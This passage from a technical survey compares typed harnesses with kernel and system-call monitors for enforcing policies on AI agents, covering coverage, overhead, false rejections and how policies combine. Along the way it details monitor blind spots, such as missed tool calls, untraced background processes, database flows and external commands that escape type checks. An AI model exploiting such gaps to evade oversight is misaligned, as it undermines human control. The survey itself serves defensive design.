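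The 15 actions exercise only four of the 15 paths: calls to web-based tool servers, calls to local tool servers, operations that a tool carries out directly from within the harness, and direct network connections. The predictions for the other 11 paths, including all those that depend on the set-up, are based only on the design analysis.

For the gateways and the harness-level controls, the runs matched the predictions:

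- The basic gateway made decisions only about calls to web-based tool servers.
- The network filter blocked both direct network actions.
- The harness-level controls checked all seven tool calls and none of the other eight actions, such as writing a file or starting a program.

The runs didn't exercise the subprocess path, so the last result doesn't contradict the prediction that harness-level controls check subprocesses. The programs the runs started apparently count as direct operations. The researchers repeated the basic gateway test with a second harness, OpenClaw, and got the same counts.

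A control in the kernel could in principle check all four of the paths in the test, and therefore all 15 actions, but ActPlane checked only seven, allowing six and stopping one. It missed all seven tool calls, and it missed one network action because of a known gap in its hooks, the points in the kernel where it attaches its checks. The harness-level controls also checked seven actions, none of which ActPlane checked.

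This is consistent with *ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026), which states only that the system checks every event that reaches one of its configured hooks. The test may understate ActPlane's performance, since it loaded on only one of the three kernel versions that Toyoda and colleagues tried. "Checked" means only that an action reached the control, and the control may still have made the wrong decision.

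### Seeing an action and understanding it

Controls that cover more paths tend to get less information about each action. Suppose the assistant pays Acme 400 euros. A monitor in the harness gets the tool's name, the recipient, the amount and the session so far. A gateway gets the full request. A kernel control can detect that a process connected to the bank's server, but not how much money it sent, so it can't enforce policy B, the daily limit on payments. It also picks up events from unrelated programs on the same computer.

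Zheng and colleagues collected 1,361 rules from the instruction files for coding agents in 64 popular software projects. About 45 percent of the rules concern events a kernel control can observe, such as running a command or writing to a certain folder. Another 38 percent require reading the contents of files, which ActPlane doesn't do. The remaining 17 percent concern matters such as how the agent explains its work.

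Even a rule about observable events may be too vague for the kernel to enforce. For example, "Run the full test suite before committing" doesn't specify which command runs the tests. ActPlane therefore lets the agent, which has read the project's files, write the concrete rule. The kernel then enforces that rule, and the agent can't weaken rules that were in place before it started.

Zheng and colleagues compared ActPlane with three controls that work at the level of tool calls, using 38 rules and 190 recorded runs, 114 of which contained a violation. ActPlane detected 77 percent of the violations, and the other controls detected 34 to 40 percent. The difference came mainly from violations inside subprocesses, where the tool call didn't show what the subprocess would do. ActPlane's misses were largely due to rules that were too narrow, and detection rose to 95 percent after a model revised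 those rules once.

The agent also has to understand the refusal. When ActPlane explained which rule the agent had broken and what to do instead, the agent complied after 98 percent of detected violations. With only the operating system's generic error message, it complied after 31 percent.

### Typed harnesses and external commands

guardscope doesn't include a typed harness, but we can ask the same question about TACIT, which checks only the Scala code that an agent submits to it. An existing agent's own tools bypass the compiler, which is why lampepfl recommends disabling them. The project also offers ATC, a ready-made coding agent built on TACIT that needs no separate agent set-up. lampepfl describes its permissions as denied by default, with temporary grants or grants for one session.

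With the other tools switched off, agent code can reach the outside world only through TACIT's library. The compiler then covers every route the code can take, as long as the effects happen in Scala. This changes when the code starts an external command:

```
requestExecPermission(Set("git")) {
  exec("git", List("diff"))
}
```

The compiler checks that the code has permission to run commands, and the library checks at runtime that `git` is on the allowlist of permitted commands. But Git isn't written in Scala and its types don't list capabilities, so the compiler can't determine which files it opens or which servers it contacts. Odersky and colleagues write that the guarantee then "degrades to that of the underlying allowlist".

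Starting a command still requires a capability, so a function inside `map` can't start one, and agent code still can't unwrap a contract to pass its text to a command. However, a command that opens files itself bypasses the library's `Classified` wrapper, so the safety of the contracts depends on which commands the list permits and which files those commands can access.

Odersky and colleagues recommend permitting only specific, safe commands. TACIT also has a strict mode that refuses common file commands such as `cat` and `rm`, so that agents use the library's file functions instead. The problem hardly affects an office assistant whose tools are all typed functions, but it matters much more for coding agents because they rely on external programs to build and test software.

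### Where system-level monitoring stops

Tether, the monitor built by Sistla and colleagues, covers much of what TACIT's compiler can't, because it records the system calls of any program that a command starts. But it stops recording when the main command ends, so it loses track of background processes. Its test results showed that it also can't follow data through databases or recognise harmful content in a file that the agent is allowed to edit. Blocking background processes and database access would close the first two gaps, much as an employer using TACIT can forbid all external commands. Neither restriction helps with harmful content, since the agent needs to edit the file to do its job.

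The current version of Tether decrypts secure web traffic only for the simulated servers in its tests. For other servers, it can identify the destination but not read what the agent sends.

Even when Tether records everything, it must infer what the system calls do. A program can copy a file in many ways, and if Tether misses one, the copy of a secret file may keep a public label. The machine-checked proofs about Tether's policies don't cover this step, because they start from the inferred actions. Sistla and colleagues therefore generated random sequences of file operations, each carried out by a randomly chosen method, and compared the monitor's decisions with the correct ones. This helped them find and fix errors, but it can't show that none remain. A typed harness doesn't have to infer effects, because its library declares them, although those declarations can also be wrong.

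### Both kinds of coverage

The path counts below come from guardscope's analysis of designs. The row for the typed harness is based on TACIT, which guardscope did not test.

| Mechanism | Which runs it covers | Which routes it covers | What it can inspect |
|---|---|---|---|
| Typed harness | all possible runs of an accepted program, before it starts | code submitted to the checker; for external commands, only the allowlist applies | the program's text and types |
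| Tool gateway | each run as it happens | 1 of 15 paths, or 3 if local tool servers are also behind it | the full tool request |
| Harness-level monitor | each run as it happens | 5 of 15 paths | tool names, arguments and the session, depending on the monitor |
| Kernel monitor | each run as it happens | 13 of 15 paths in theory; ActPlane checked 7 of 15 test actions | files, network addresses and process history |

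## What does each method cost?

Odersky and colleagues write that a type system "imposes no monitoring overhead". This is right in the narrow sense that the Scala compiler removes capture sets before a program runs, so they take no time during the run. But the harness has to compile every program first, and the model has to rewrite the ones that the compiler rejects. TACIT's library also makes some checks during the run, such as whether a path lies inside the permitted directory. A fair comparison with monitors has to include all of this, along with the tokens each method uses, the tasks that fail because of it and the work of setting it up.

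### Compile time and retries

TACIT's compiler checks a typical program in under a second, once the Java virtual machine it runs on has warmed up. A rejection adds more overhead than the check, because the model has to read the error message and write the program again. Odersky and colleagues counted these retries on τ²-bench, the customer service benchmark. In the table below, the last column is the product of the two before it.

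| Model | Domain | Programs needing a retry | Mean retries for those programs | Extra generations per program |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek V3.2 | Airline | 7.93% | 1.39 | 0.110 |
| | Retail | 1.57% | 1.25 | 0.020 |
| gpt-oss-120b | Airline | 1.58% | 1.36 | 0.021 |
| | Retail | 0.32% | 1.22 | 0.004 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Airline | 1.43% | 1.26 | 0.018 |
| | Retail | 0.33% | 1.06 | 0.003 |

In the worst of the six cases, the model wrote 11 extra programs for every hundred. In the other five, it wrote about two or fewer. The recurring errors were ordinary slips, such as forgetting that a value might be null or putting a dollar sign in text where Scala reads it as the start of a variable.

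Retries were also rare in ELBA, the Haskell system. Zhou and colleagues tested it with four newer models: Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, Sonnet 5 and GPT 5.4. A run could contain several programs but needed 0.13 retries on average, and retries took up 3.4 percent of the running time. In 7 of 2,688 runs, the model used up its retries without producing a program that passed the checker.

ELBA's runs took about three times as long as CaMeL's, but type checking accounts for little of the difference. CaMeL writes one program at the start, while ELBA calls the model again to write new programs after reading some data.

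### Task scores with typed programs

Writing typed programs might also make an agent worse at its job. Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT with ordinary tool calls on τ²-bench, running each task ten times. The table gives the share of tasks solved.

| Model | Airline, tool calls | Airline, TACIT | Retail, tool calls | Retail, TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% | 53.3% | 57.0% |
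| MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% | 74.6% | 75.5% |

Odersky and colleagues also tested TACIT on SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software issues from GitHub that an agent has to fix. MiniMax M2.5 solved 43.3 percent with ordinary tools and 41.7 percent with TACIT, a difference of five issues that could easily be chance. They suggest that coding tasks depend more on shell commands, which are less natural to express through TACIT's library.

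TACIT scored higher in all six comparisons on τ²-bench, and Odersky and colleagues credit the typed results and the compiler's error messages. However, the agents with TACIT also wrote whole programs instead of single calls, and Patel and colleagues found that most models do at least as well with programs even when nothing checks the types. A third group of agents writing unchecked programs would have separated the two effects. The results are good evidence that writing typed programs doesn't make these agents noticeably worse, but only weak evidence that the types themselves help.

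Programs can also save far more computation than checking them takes. Zhou and colleagues gave 100 bibliography tasks to ELBA and to an ordinary agent with a web search tool. The ordinary agent made about 4 times as many model calls, and used 2.5 times as many output tokens and 65 times as many input tokens. This comparison has the same weakness, since the two agents also had different tools.

### How long monitors take

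A monitor that only evaluates a rule is very fast. For an agent that writes code, Wang and colleagues measured 1.42 milliseconds to parse AgentSpec's rules and 2.83 milliseconds to evaluate the conditions. The agent's average run took 25.4 seconds, so even a thousand evaluations would add less than 3 seconds. These figures exclude the time spent responding to a violation. Stopping the agent takes almost no time, but asking the user means waiting for an answer, and having the model reconsider takes another model call.

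*ProbGuard* (2025) describes a more elaborate monitor that predicts how likely the agent is to stay safe and intervenes when the probability falls too low. This monitor also adds only milliseconds. Monitors become slow mainly when they call a language model. *VIGIL* (2026), a system that enforces rules on how agents use skills (packaged instructions for particular kinds of task), adds 4.38 seconds per run. One model call, which translates the rules into a form a solver can check, takes 92.5 percent of that time, and the check itself takes 0.27 seconds. The added time doesn't grow with the length of the run, and the harness could store the translation for reuse.

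Kamath and colleagues timed whole tasks instead of single checks. They ran Qwen3-32B on the ordinary tasks of τ-bench with Agent-C, with AgentSpec, with DynaGuard (a language model that judges each action) and with no monitor:

| Monitor | Seconds per task | Peak GPU memory |
|---|---|---|
| None | 333 | 67.7 GB |
| AgentSpec | 409 | 67.7 GB |
| Agent-C | 480 | 69.7 GB |
| DynaGuard | 494 | 81.4 GB |

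Checks that take a few milliseconds can't account for the 76 seconds AgentSpec added. The agent probably spent most of that time on what it did after refusals, including finishing tasks it would otherwise have got wrong. A better measure is total time divided by the number of tasks the agent completes correctly and within the rules. Combining these times with the success rates, weighted by the number of tasks in each domain, gives about 1,450 seconds without a monitor and about 1,000 with Agent-C. By that measure, Agent-C saves time, at least with a model that breaks the rules as often as this one.

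Tether has a different kind of overhead because it traces every command. It runs an approved command only once, but Sistla and colleagues did the tracing with strace, a standard tool whose significant overhead slowed their experiments. They suggest replacing strace with a faster mechanism. Their prototype also evaluates policies directly in Lean, and they propose a compiled version for systems that need more speed.

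### Extra tokens

CaMeL's main overhead is extra tokens. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) compared several defences on AgentDojo using GPT-4o, and CaMeL used the most tokens. On the median task, it needed 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an agent with no defence. These figures cover CaMeL's whole two-model design. Attaching labels to values in an interpreter uses no tokens by itself.

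When Agent-C refuses a faulty call, the number of extra tokens used depends on whether it can go back to the start of that call or has to resend the whole prompt, as it does with closed models. Kamath and colleagues compared the two procedures using Qwen3-8B on the airline tasks. Resending the prompt raised the average input from 3,885 to 6,522 tokens each time the harness called the agent, and the average output from 415 to 899. Agent-C discarded 498 of those 899 output tokens, compared with 23 of 415 when it could go back. Agent-C still enforced every rule when it resent the prompt, but the agent completed slightly fewer tasks.

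### The Verifier Tax

The highest estimates of monitoring overhead come from *The Verifier Tax* (Sah, Sah and colleagues, 2026), the source of the term that Dantas and colleagues use. The experiment covered 165 airline and retail tasks from τ-bench, each run three times with every combination of two small models, GPT-OSS-20B and GLM-4-9B, and three designs, for 2,970 runs in all. In the simplest design, the model calls tools directly. In the second, called Triad, the same model also acts as a planner, which chooses the next step, and a verifier, which accepts or rejects each action. The third, Triad-Safety, adds the company's rules to the verifier's instructions. If the verifier rejects three attempts in a row, the harness carries out the last one anyway, which happened in only 28 runs.

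Few runs with a verifier ended in a correct result within the rules, but the agents did no better without one:

| Model and domain | Direct calls: all successes | of which within the rules | Triad-Safety: all successes | of which within the rules | Tokens, relative to direct calls |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-OSS-20B, airline | 22.7% | 0.0% | 23.3% | 0.0% | 2.8 times |
| GPT-OSS-20B, retail | 21.2% | 0.0% | 21.5% | 0.6% | 2.6 times |
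| GLM-4-9B, airline | 28.7% | 0.7% | 25.3% | 4.7% | 2.2 times |
| GLM-4-9B, retail | 4.9% | 2.6% | 5.5% | 2.9% | 2.0 times |

These percentages are shares of all tasks. The verifier used a lot of tokens and achieved little, but it did not turn safe successes into failures, because there were hardly any to begin with. Monitoring does not account for the whole increase in tokens, since Triad and Triad-Safety also add a planner. Adding the company's rules to the verifier's instructions made little difference to token use.

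The verifier reportedly intercepted 94.1 percent of forbidden actions for GPT-OSS-20B on the retail tasks, which is hard to reconcile with the other results. An audit after the retail runs found an invented identifier, such as a made-up customer name, in 93.7 percent of runs across the three designs. Yet the paper reports only 157 interventions in the 345 retail runs with Triad-Safety. If violations were about as common in that design as in the others, the verifier must have missed most of what the audit found, so the interception rate probably covers only the kinds of violation it could detect.

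Sah and colleagues also measured how often a run still succeeded after a block. In their summary, they report 21 percent for GPT-OSS-20B on airline tasks and nearly zero on retail tasks. For blocks based on the safety rules, they report 16.7 percent on airline tasks in their results table but 32 percent of 25 cases in their discussion. The zero for retail is based on three cases.

These rates look less alarming because the models also did badly at these tasks when the verifier didn't block them. Across both Triad designs, 21.3 percent of runs with neither a rejection nor a tool error succeeded, compared with 18.7 percent of runs with only rejections and 7.7 percent of runs with both rejections and tool errors.

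The study is therefore mostly about small models that check their own work. Reddy and colleagues' gates need no model calls, and agents completed more tasks with them. Sah and colleagues recommend a similar approach, in which code checks that every identifier in a tool call appeared in an earlier result.

### When is a static check cheaper?

A simple model of waiting time helps to compare the two methods. Let c be the time to check a program, r the expected number of retries, g the time the model takes to write the program again, n the number of actions in the run and d the monitor's delay per action:

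```
static cost     = c + r × (g + c)
monitoring cost = n × d
```

DeepSeek's airline figures, the worst of the six, give r = 0.0793 × 1.39, or about 0.11. Suppose that a check takes 1 second, slightly more than Odersky and colleagues report, and that rewriting a program takes 10 seconds. The static cost per program is then:

```
1 + 0.11 × (10 + 1) = 2.21 seconds
```

Dividing this by the delay per action gives the number of actions at which the static check starts to take less total time than runtime monitoring. The first delay below is AgentSpec's, and the other two are assumptions.

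| Monitor | Delay per action | Static check cheaper from |
|---|---|---|
| Rule in ordinary code | 2.83 milliseconds | about 780 actions |
| Slower check, such as one that traces a command | 0.1 seconds | 23 actions |
| Language model as judge | 2 seconds | 2 actions |

At MiniMax M2.5's retry rate on retail tasks, the static overhead falls to 1.04 seconds and the thresholds fall to about 370, 11 and 1 actions.

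The office assistant's program takes six actions if it pays the invoice. A monitor with simple rules would add 17 milliseconds, the static check 2.21 seconds and a model judge 12 seconds. If the program instead read, paid and filed receipts for 300 invoices, it would take 900 actions. The static check would then add only about a third of a second less than the simple rules. Speed is therefore a poor reason to choose types over simple rules, though it can be a good reason to choose them over a model that judges every action.

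Refusals change the result more than the checks do. Suppose the monitor wrongly blocks one action in a thousand and each refusal requires 10 seconds of rewriting. This adds an average of 10 milliseconds per action, over three times the delay of the rule itself, and lowers the first threshold from about 780 actions to about 170.

The comparison also applies only when either method could enforce the policy alone. For policy B, the daily payment limit, the harness has to keep a running total even if the developer adds a type checker, so the developer then has the overhead of both methods.

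### Why older systems had different costs

Older research on security and types often reports much larger or more carefully measured slowdowns, because the mechanisms it studied ran checks far more often. For example, software fault isolation confines untrusted code by adding instructions around its memory writes and jumps. Wahbe, Lucco and colleagues introduced it in 1993 and measured an average slowdown of about 4 percent. WebAssembly is a related, more recent format for running compiled programs safely in browsers. In 2019 Jangda, Powers and colleagues found that standard benchmark programs ran 45 to 55 percent slower in WebAssembly than as ordinary compiled code, though not all of that slowdown came from safety checks.

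Types can slow programs down too. Gradual typing mixes typed and untyped code, and the system checks values at run time as they pass between the two. Takikawa, Feltey and colleagues showed in 2016 that some partly typed Racket programs ran more than 100 times slower than the untyped versions. TACIT avoids run-time checks on capture sets because the compiler examines all of the agent's code before it runs.

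An agent may call a tool once every few seconds and then wait for a model to respond, so a check that adds several milliseconds to each call is unnoticeable. The same delay would be unacceptable on memory writes, which a program may perform millions of times a second. At that rate, even a few extra instructions per write add up.

### False rejections

Both methods sometimes refuse harmless work, but there is no common measure of how often. TACIT's retry rate of 0.32 to 7.93 percent includes programs that really were faulty, so it is not a rate of false rejections. It also omits useful programs that a model may avoid writing because it knows the checker would reject them. That harm appears only as a task done badly or not at all.

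How often a monitor raises false alarms depends heavily on its rules. Tether blocked 4.7 percent of harmless runs with a policy that its developers had refined on the same benchmarks. By contrast, *Stale Does Not Mean Unsafe* (2026) cites another paper, *Formal runtime verification for tool-using LLM agents*, in which generic rules about the order of actions fired on 29.3 percent of harmless runs.

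Wang and colleagues also tested AgentSpec on a simulated household robot. With the rules on, the robot carried out none of the hazardous instructions, but its success rate on safe tasks fell from 58.6 to 54.3 percent. When they had a language model write the rules, one rule against spilling liquids banned all pouring, so the robot could no longer water a plant.

A strict policy can reduce an agent's usefulness more than all the retries and delays together. ELBA checks its information-flow policies at run time. When Zhou and colleagues turned these policies on, Opus 4.7 completed 10 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks, down from 18. With a type checker that enforced equally strict rules, the agent would probably fail many of the same tasks.

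A monitor's refusal can also leave work half done. If it stops a program after 60 of 100 payments, the next program has to work out which invoices remain, and a mistake could mean paying a supplier twice. A false rejection by a monitor can therefore do much more harm than one by a compiler, even if both are equally rare.

### The work of setting it up

Someone has to write the rules or the types before either method works. The reusable part of TACIT is about 1,000 lines of Scala, and writing it requires an understanding of capture checking. Each new set of tools also needs typed declarations. These took a few hundred lines each for the airline and the shop, about as many as the JSON descriptions they replaced. Odersky and colleagues say that agents can help write the declarations, but that people should review them before an agent uses them. ELBA takes more work, since the developer has to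 write the whole application in Haskell.

Monitor rules can be short, and Wang and colleagues needed only one for each of their 25 categories of risky code. In a separate test, rules written by OpenAI's o1, an older model, caught 87 percent of the risky code. The rest got through partly because o1 had followed its examples too closely. For instance, a rule to protect configuration files covered only the files named in the examples.

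Agent-C needs formal rules about the order of calls, which take more expertise to write. Kamath and colleagues had Claude Sonnet 4.5 translate the shop's written policy into such rules. An agent based on Qwen3-8B completed 42.1 percent of tasks and broke no rules, whether it used the translated rules or handwritten ones. Claude had added some unnecessary checks, but they did no harm in this test.

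Tether's policy has 24 rules and long lists of protected paths and exceptions. Sistla and colleagues compare refining it to the work on SELinux, an access control system for Linux. The security community took around five years to develop practical SELinux policies. After each revision of Tether's policy, proofs in Lean confirmed that the most important guarantees still held. Each new task also needs its own list of sensitive files and permitted websites.

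## Does safety survive when parts and methods are combined?

The office assistant might use a payment library from one team, a summarising tool from another, several monitors, and a second agent that checks invoices. Checking these parts separately saves a lot of work, but it helps only if parts that are safe alone are also safe together. This holds for policies such as the payment limit, but it can fail for policies against leaks.

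### What a signature makes possible

Suppose a library offers a helper that removes the spaces around a text before passing it to a function:

```
def onTrimmed[U](f: String => U, x: String): U = f(x.trim)
```

The signature, the part before the equals sign, gives the types of the arguments and the result. The library must also declare any capabilities it uses itself, and this one uses none. The compiler checks the helper's body against these declarations once. If someone later adds a line that writes to a log file, the compiler rejects the library until it declares the log.

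To check a program that uses the helper, the compiler needs only the signature:

```
contract.map(text => onTrimmed(shout, text))   // accepted
contract.map(text => onTrimmed(store, text))   // rejected
```

As before, `shout` converts text to capitals and `store` writes it to a file. The second line fails because the type of `store` lists `file`, so the function passed to `map` isn't pure. If the developer rewrites the helper's body but keeps its signature, both results stay the same.

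Without signatures, an analysis has to follow functions and data through the whole program. The standard method for this is a family of analyses called kCFA, where k is the number of recent calls the analysis remembers. Suppose a program uses the helper twice on ordinary values:

```
onTrimmed(shout, contract_text)
onTrimmed(store, note)
```

With k = 0, the analysis merges the two calls, so `f` may be `shout` or `store` and `x` may be the contract or the note. It therefore cannot rule out that `store` receives the contract. With k = 1, it analyzes the calls separately and avoids this false alarm.

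The extra precision requires a lot of computation. *Deciding kCFA is complete for EXPTIME* (Van Horn and Mairson, 2013; first presented in 2008) proved that the analysis takes polynomial time for k = 0 but is EXPTIME-complete for every fixed k above zero. The difficulty comes from functions that use variables from the surrounding program, because the analysis records the context in which each variable got its value. With 100 possible contexts and 10 such variables, a single function can have up to 100^10, or 10^20, combinations. Remembering more calls doesn't move the problem into a higher class, because exponential time is enough for any fixed k (*The Complexity of Flow Analysis in Higher-Order Languages*, 2013).

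These are worst cases, and an agent's 30-line program may be quick to analyse, although the analysis would have to include the library code it calls. Van Horn and Mairson point out that type inference for the language ML is also complete for exponential time, which has hardly bothered programmers, but they add that flow analysis has been slow in practice as well. For agents, the more dependable advantage of signatures is that the compiler doesn't have to check the library again for each new program, when an agent may write hundreds of programs a day against the same library.

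### Smaller permissions for sub-agents

An agent can hand part of its work to another agent. Odersky and colleagues suggest that the outer agent grant such a sub-agent a subset of its own capabilities, so that the compiler rejects any sub-agent code that exceeds them. LACUNA, the system in which running programs call a model for more code, already has most of what this requires. Suppose the assistant holds three capabilities: `invoices` for the invoice directory, `net` for the network and `payments` for the bank. It could delegate a check like this:

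```
val audit: String ->{invoices} String =
  name => local.agent[String](s"check the sums in $name")
```

The type limits `audit` to `invoices`. LACUNA compiles the sub-agent's code inside this function, so the compiler would reject code that contacted a website, because that code would add `net` to the capture set. If the sub-agent calls a third agent, that agent's code is inside the same function and has the same limit.

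The type annotation is essential. Zhao and colleagues explain that a nested call normally has access to everything the outer call had, plus whatever the outer code has defined since. Sub-agents therefore start with more access than their parents had unless someone narrows their permissions.

Giving sub-agents fewer capabilities also doesn't by itself limit how much they can spend in total. If the assistant passes `payments` to five sub-agents, they share one counter, so together they can pay each recipient at most 1,000 euros. If the library gave each sub-agent a new counter, together they could pay the same recipient 5,000 euros.

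One of LACUNA's guarantees weakens when calls are nested. Rejected code still has no effects, but the outer program is already running when it calls a sub-agent. If the outer program has made a payment and the sub-agent then runs out of retries, the payment stands.

Nested calls work in practice. Zhao and colleagues ran LACUNA on BrowseComp-Plus, a benchmark of difficult research questions over a fixed collection of documents. With DeepSeek-V4-Flash, it averaged 5.9 rounds and 15.5 searches per question, and the compiler rejected 8.6 percent of the generated code. The test did not include attacks on sub-agents with reduced permissions. Odersky and colleagues leave a full evaluation with several agents to future work.

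### Combining monitors

Two safety properties combined are also a safety property, because a run that violates the combination violates at least one of the two, and that violation is detectable after finitely many actions. A harness can therefore run a monitor for each property and carry out an action only if both monitors allow it.

The monitors should update their records only after both have allowed a payment. Suppose one enforces the daily limit and the other requires a manager's approval for payments above 500 euros. The assistant tries to pay 600 euros without approval. If the first monitor adds the 600 euros to its total before the second blocks the payment, it will later wrongly block a payment of 450 euros, even though the 600 euros were never paid.

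Requiring an assistant to follow two policies at once preserves safety but can prevent it from doing useful work. If one team's policy requires an order before each payment and another's requires a payment before each order, the assistant can do neither. When monitors can change actions, the sequence in which they run also matters. If one monitor checks an email and a second one then attaches a file, the file goes unchecked.

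Allowing an action when either policy allows it is riskier. Suppose one policy lets an agent read contracts but not send email, and another lets it send email but not read contracts. Neither policy alone would let it email a contract. Under the combination, the agent can read a contract because the first policy allows it, then email the text because the second does.

Tether, the monitor that infers actions from system calls, supports both kinds of combination, with the keywords `require` and `grant`. In simplified form, it decides as follows:

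```
allow an action if
    every required policy allows it, and
    no matching local rule denies it, and
    a local rule, the default or a granted policy allows it
```

A granted policy counts only when no local rule matches the action, so it can't override one. Sistla and colleagues proved four properties of this scheme in Lean:

- If a required policy denies an action, no local rule, default or granted policy can allow it.
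- Adding permissive local rules never undoes a local denial.
- The order in which someone writes the rules and policies makes no difference.
- A refused action leaves Tether's record of labels and privileges unchanged, which avoids the problem with the 600 euros.

A company could therefore require a policy against uploading sensitive files and let each team add its own rules. A team that allows uploads to its own website still couldn't upload a sensitive file there. Tether's benchmark tests are set up this way, with four required policies of 7, 6, 10 and 1 rules. The proofs show that nothing added later weakens a required policy, but not that the policy is strict enough.

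### Why two leak-free programs can leak together

The argument for safety properties looks at one run at a time, so it doesn't carry over to noninterference. Suppose two programs share a secret random bit, `key`, and `penalty` is 1 if a classified contract has a penalty clause and 0 otherwise:

```
publish(penalty XOR key)    # program 1
publish(key)                # program 2
```

XOR gives 0 if two bits are equal and 1 if they differ. Program 1 publishes 0 or 1 with equal probability whatever the contract contains, so its output alone reveals nothing about the contract. Program 2 doesn't use the contract. But an outsider who sees both outputs learns whether the contract has a penalty clause, because the outputs differ exactly when it does.

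*Noninterference Analysis of Irreversible Systems and Reversible Systems* (2025) examines several definitions of noninterference for systems with random behaviour. Only three are preserved under at least one of the usual ways of combining systems. For two of those three, running systems side by side is safe only if they coordinate solely through public actions, which rules out sharing a secret key. None is preserved under a free choice between two secure systems. For example, one system might only be able to send a public "ready" message, and the other only to perform a secret action. If a combined system can do either, an outsider who finds that "ready" is no longer available learns that the secret action has happened.

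Components can still be combined safely if their interfaces are detailed enough. In *Information-Flow Interfaces* (2020), each component's interface lists the information flows that the component prevents and those that it relies on its surroundings to prevent. Program 1's interface would require that `key` never reaches an outsider. Program 2 can't guarantee this, so the mismatch shows up before the two are run together. If the interfaces are compatible, any components that satisfy them produce only flows that the combined interface allows. *Hypercontracts* (2021) describes policies as sets of acceptable components rather than sets of acceptable runs. It also defines an operation, similar to division, that takes the requirement for a whole system and the specification of one part and calculates what the missing part must satisfy.

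Type systems avoid the problem by being stricter than noninterference. Under the rules of Volpano and colleagues, `penalty XOR key` is secret because it contains a secret, so the checker rejects program 1 even when it is checked alone. This is a false rejection if nobody publishes the key. But if the checker accepts two programs with the same secrecy levels, it also accepts them run one after the other.

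### Writing the checks into the program

Static and run-time methods can also share the work on one program. Erlingsson and Schneider's system SASI rewrote Java programs so that they contained their own security checks and stopped before a violation. Hamlen (2006), in *Security Policy Enforcement by Automated Program-Rewriting*, explains that such a rewriter can also analyse the program and leave out checks that would always succeed. Suppose the employer adds a limit of 500 euros on any single payment. Part of the assistant's program could then become:

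```
if invoice.amount <= 400:
    check_daily_total(invoice.recipient, invoice.amount)
    pay(invoice.recipient, invoice.amount)
```

The rewriter doesn't need to add a check for the new limit, because the amount is at most 400 euros on this branch. The check for policy B must stay because it depends on the invoice and the day's earlier payments. Static analysis makes the program faster by avoiding unnecessary checks, and the run-time check covers what the analysis can't determine. Checks inside the program can also use information that an outside monitor lacks, such as which of its own functions the program has called.

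A faulty rewriter might leave out a check that the program needs. Hamlen therefore built Mobile, a system for Microsoft's .NET in which nobody has to trust the rewriter. The rewriter adds both checks and type annotations. A smaller, trusted type checker then uses the annotations to verify that the result obeys the policy, and rejects it otherwise. An agent harness could use the same arrangement and let the language model insert the checks, because a missing check would only cause the type checker to reject the program. Mobile doesn't cover information-flow policies.

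Proof-carrying code generalises this idea by replacing the type annotations with a logical proof. The proof could show, for example, that every path to `pay` first calls `check_daily_total` with the same recipient and amount. The day's total would come from the check itself rather than from the proof.

### The border with untyped code

Some parts of an agent system will have no types, such as an older Python plug-in that reads invoices. Gradual typing would check whatever the plug-in returns at the point where typed code receives it. If that is an invoice, the program can check immediately that the amount is a number. A returned function has to be wrapped so that the result of each call is checked, which can slow some programs considerably. Hybrid type checking accepts code it can prove safe, rejects code it can prove unsafe and inserts run-time checks for the rest.

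Capabilities are harder to check at such a border. A function's capture set isn't available at runtime, so no quick test can show that a Python function is pure. On the typed side, the function must be treated as if it may hold any capability, so `map` will refuse it. Alternatively, the harness can run the function in a separate process without tools, as it could for `sealed_map`, so that process isolation restricts the Python code while the types still protect the typed code.

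### Verifying the monitor's rules beforehand

Tether applies a static method to the monitor's policy and leaves the agent's programs unchecked until they run. The developer specifies a starting state and a bad state, and a language model tries to prove that no sequence of allowed actions leads from one to the other. Lean checks the proof. If the policy has a flaw, the model instead looks for a sequence of actions that reaches the bad state.

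One guarantee is that secret data never enters the model's context. The proof is by induction, showing that the start is safe and that each allowed action keeps it safe. The context starts with nothing secret, and only 2 of Tether's 11 kinds of action can raise its label, reading a resource and receiving data from the network. The policy denies both when the data is secret, so the label stays below "secret" after any number of actions. Sistla and colleagues proved seven such guarantees for their benchmark policy. The proof covers every sequence of allowed actions, and the monitor keeps actual runs within those sequences, whatever language the agent uses.

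*LEANGUARD* (2026) describes another monitor with policies in Lean. On τ²-bench, agents without the monitor carried out at least 33 forbidden calls that changed something, in 28 conversations. With the monitor, none of the 1,702 calls it stopped took effect, but this count overstates the harm prevented because it includes every attempt across two versions of the monitor. Agents solved 72.7 percent of tasks without a monitor. They solved 70.9 percent when the monitor explained its refusals, a difference that could be due to chance, and 68.9 percent when it refused without an explanation, a statistically significant drop.

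### TACIT as a combination

TACIT also depends on both methods, although its main argument is about types. The compiler establishes which kinds of access a program has, and run-time code checks the details:

| Resource | Checked by the compiler | Handled at run time |
|---|---|---|
| Files | the program holds a `FileSystem` and doesn't keep it after its block ends | whether each path lies in the permitted directory |
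| Network | the program holds a `Network` | whether each host is on the list |
| External commands | the program holds permission to run commands | whether each command is on the list |
| Exceptions | no exception contains a capability | the harness catches exceptions and can wrap them |

The compiler's checks and the run-time checks are both needed. The compiler stops a program from keeping its access too long or using it inside `map`, while the run-time checks stop permission to open one directory from becoming permission to open them all. Odersky and colleagues regard run-time policies as complementary to capabilities.

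### An office assistant with all the layers

The assistant's three policies need different mechanisms, and a developer could combine them as follows.

**Types for policy A.** As in TACIT, contracts arrive as `Classified` values. The payment tool needs a capability and accepts only ordinary numbers:

```
def pay(to: Account, euros: Int)(using Payments^): PaymentId
```

Agent code therefore can't call `pay` inside `map`, and it can't encode a contract in the amount of a payment, because anything it computes from a contract stays wrapped.

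To enforce policy B, the `Payments` capability gives access to a payment service that keeps a total for each recipient and day. The service rejects zero or negative amounts and payments that would push the total over the limit. These refusals don't weaken policy A, because they depend only on earlier payments, which can't depend on a contract.

**A retrying service for policy C.** No gate can make sure that a receipt eventually follows, so the payment service files the receipt itself:

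1. It saves the request to disk with a unique number.
2. It sends the payment to the bank, and repeats the request with the same number if no answer comes. The bank ignores repeats of a number it has already processed.
3. It saves the bank's transaction number.
4. It files the receipt, and tries again until the accounting system accepts it.

If the service crashes, it restarts and continues from the last step it saved. The agent's program can fail at any point after making its request without affecting the receipt.

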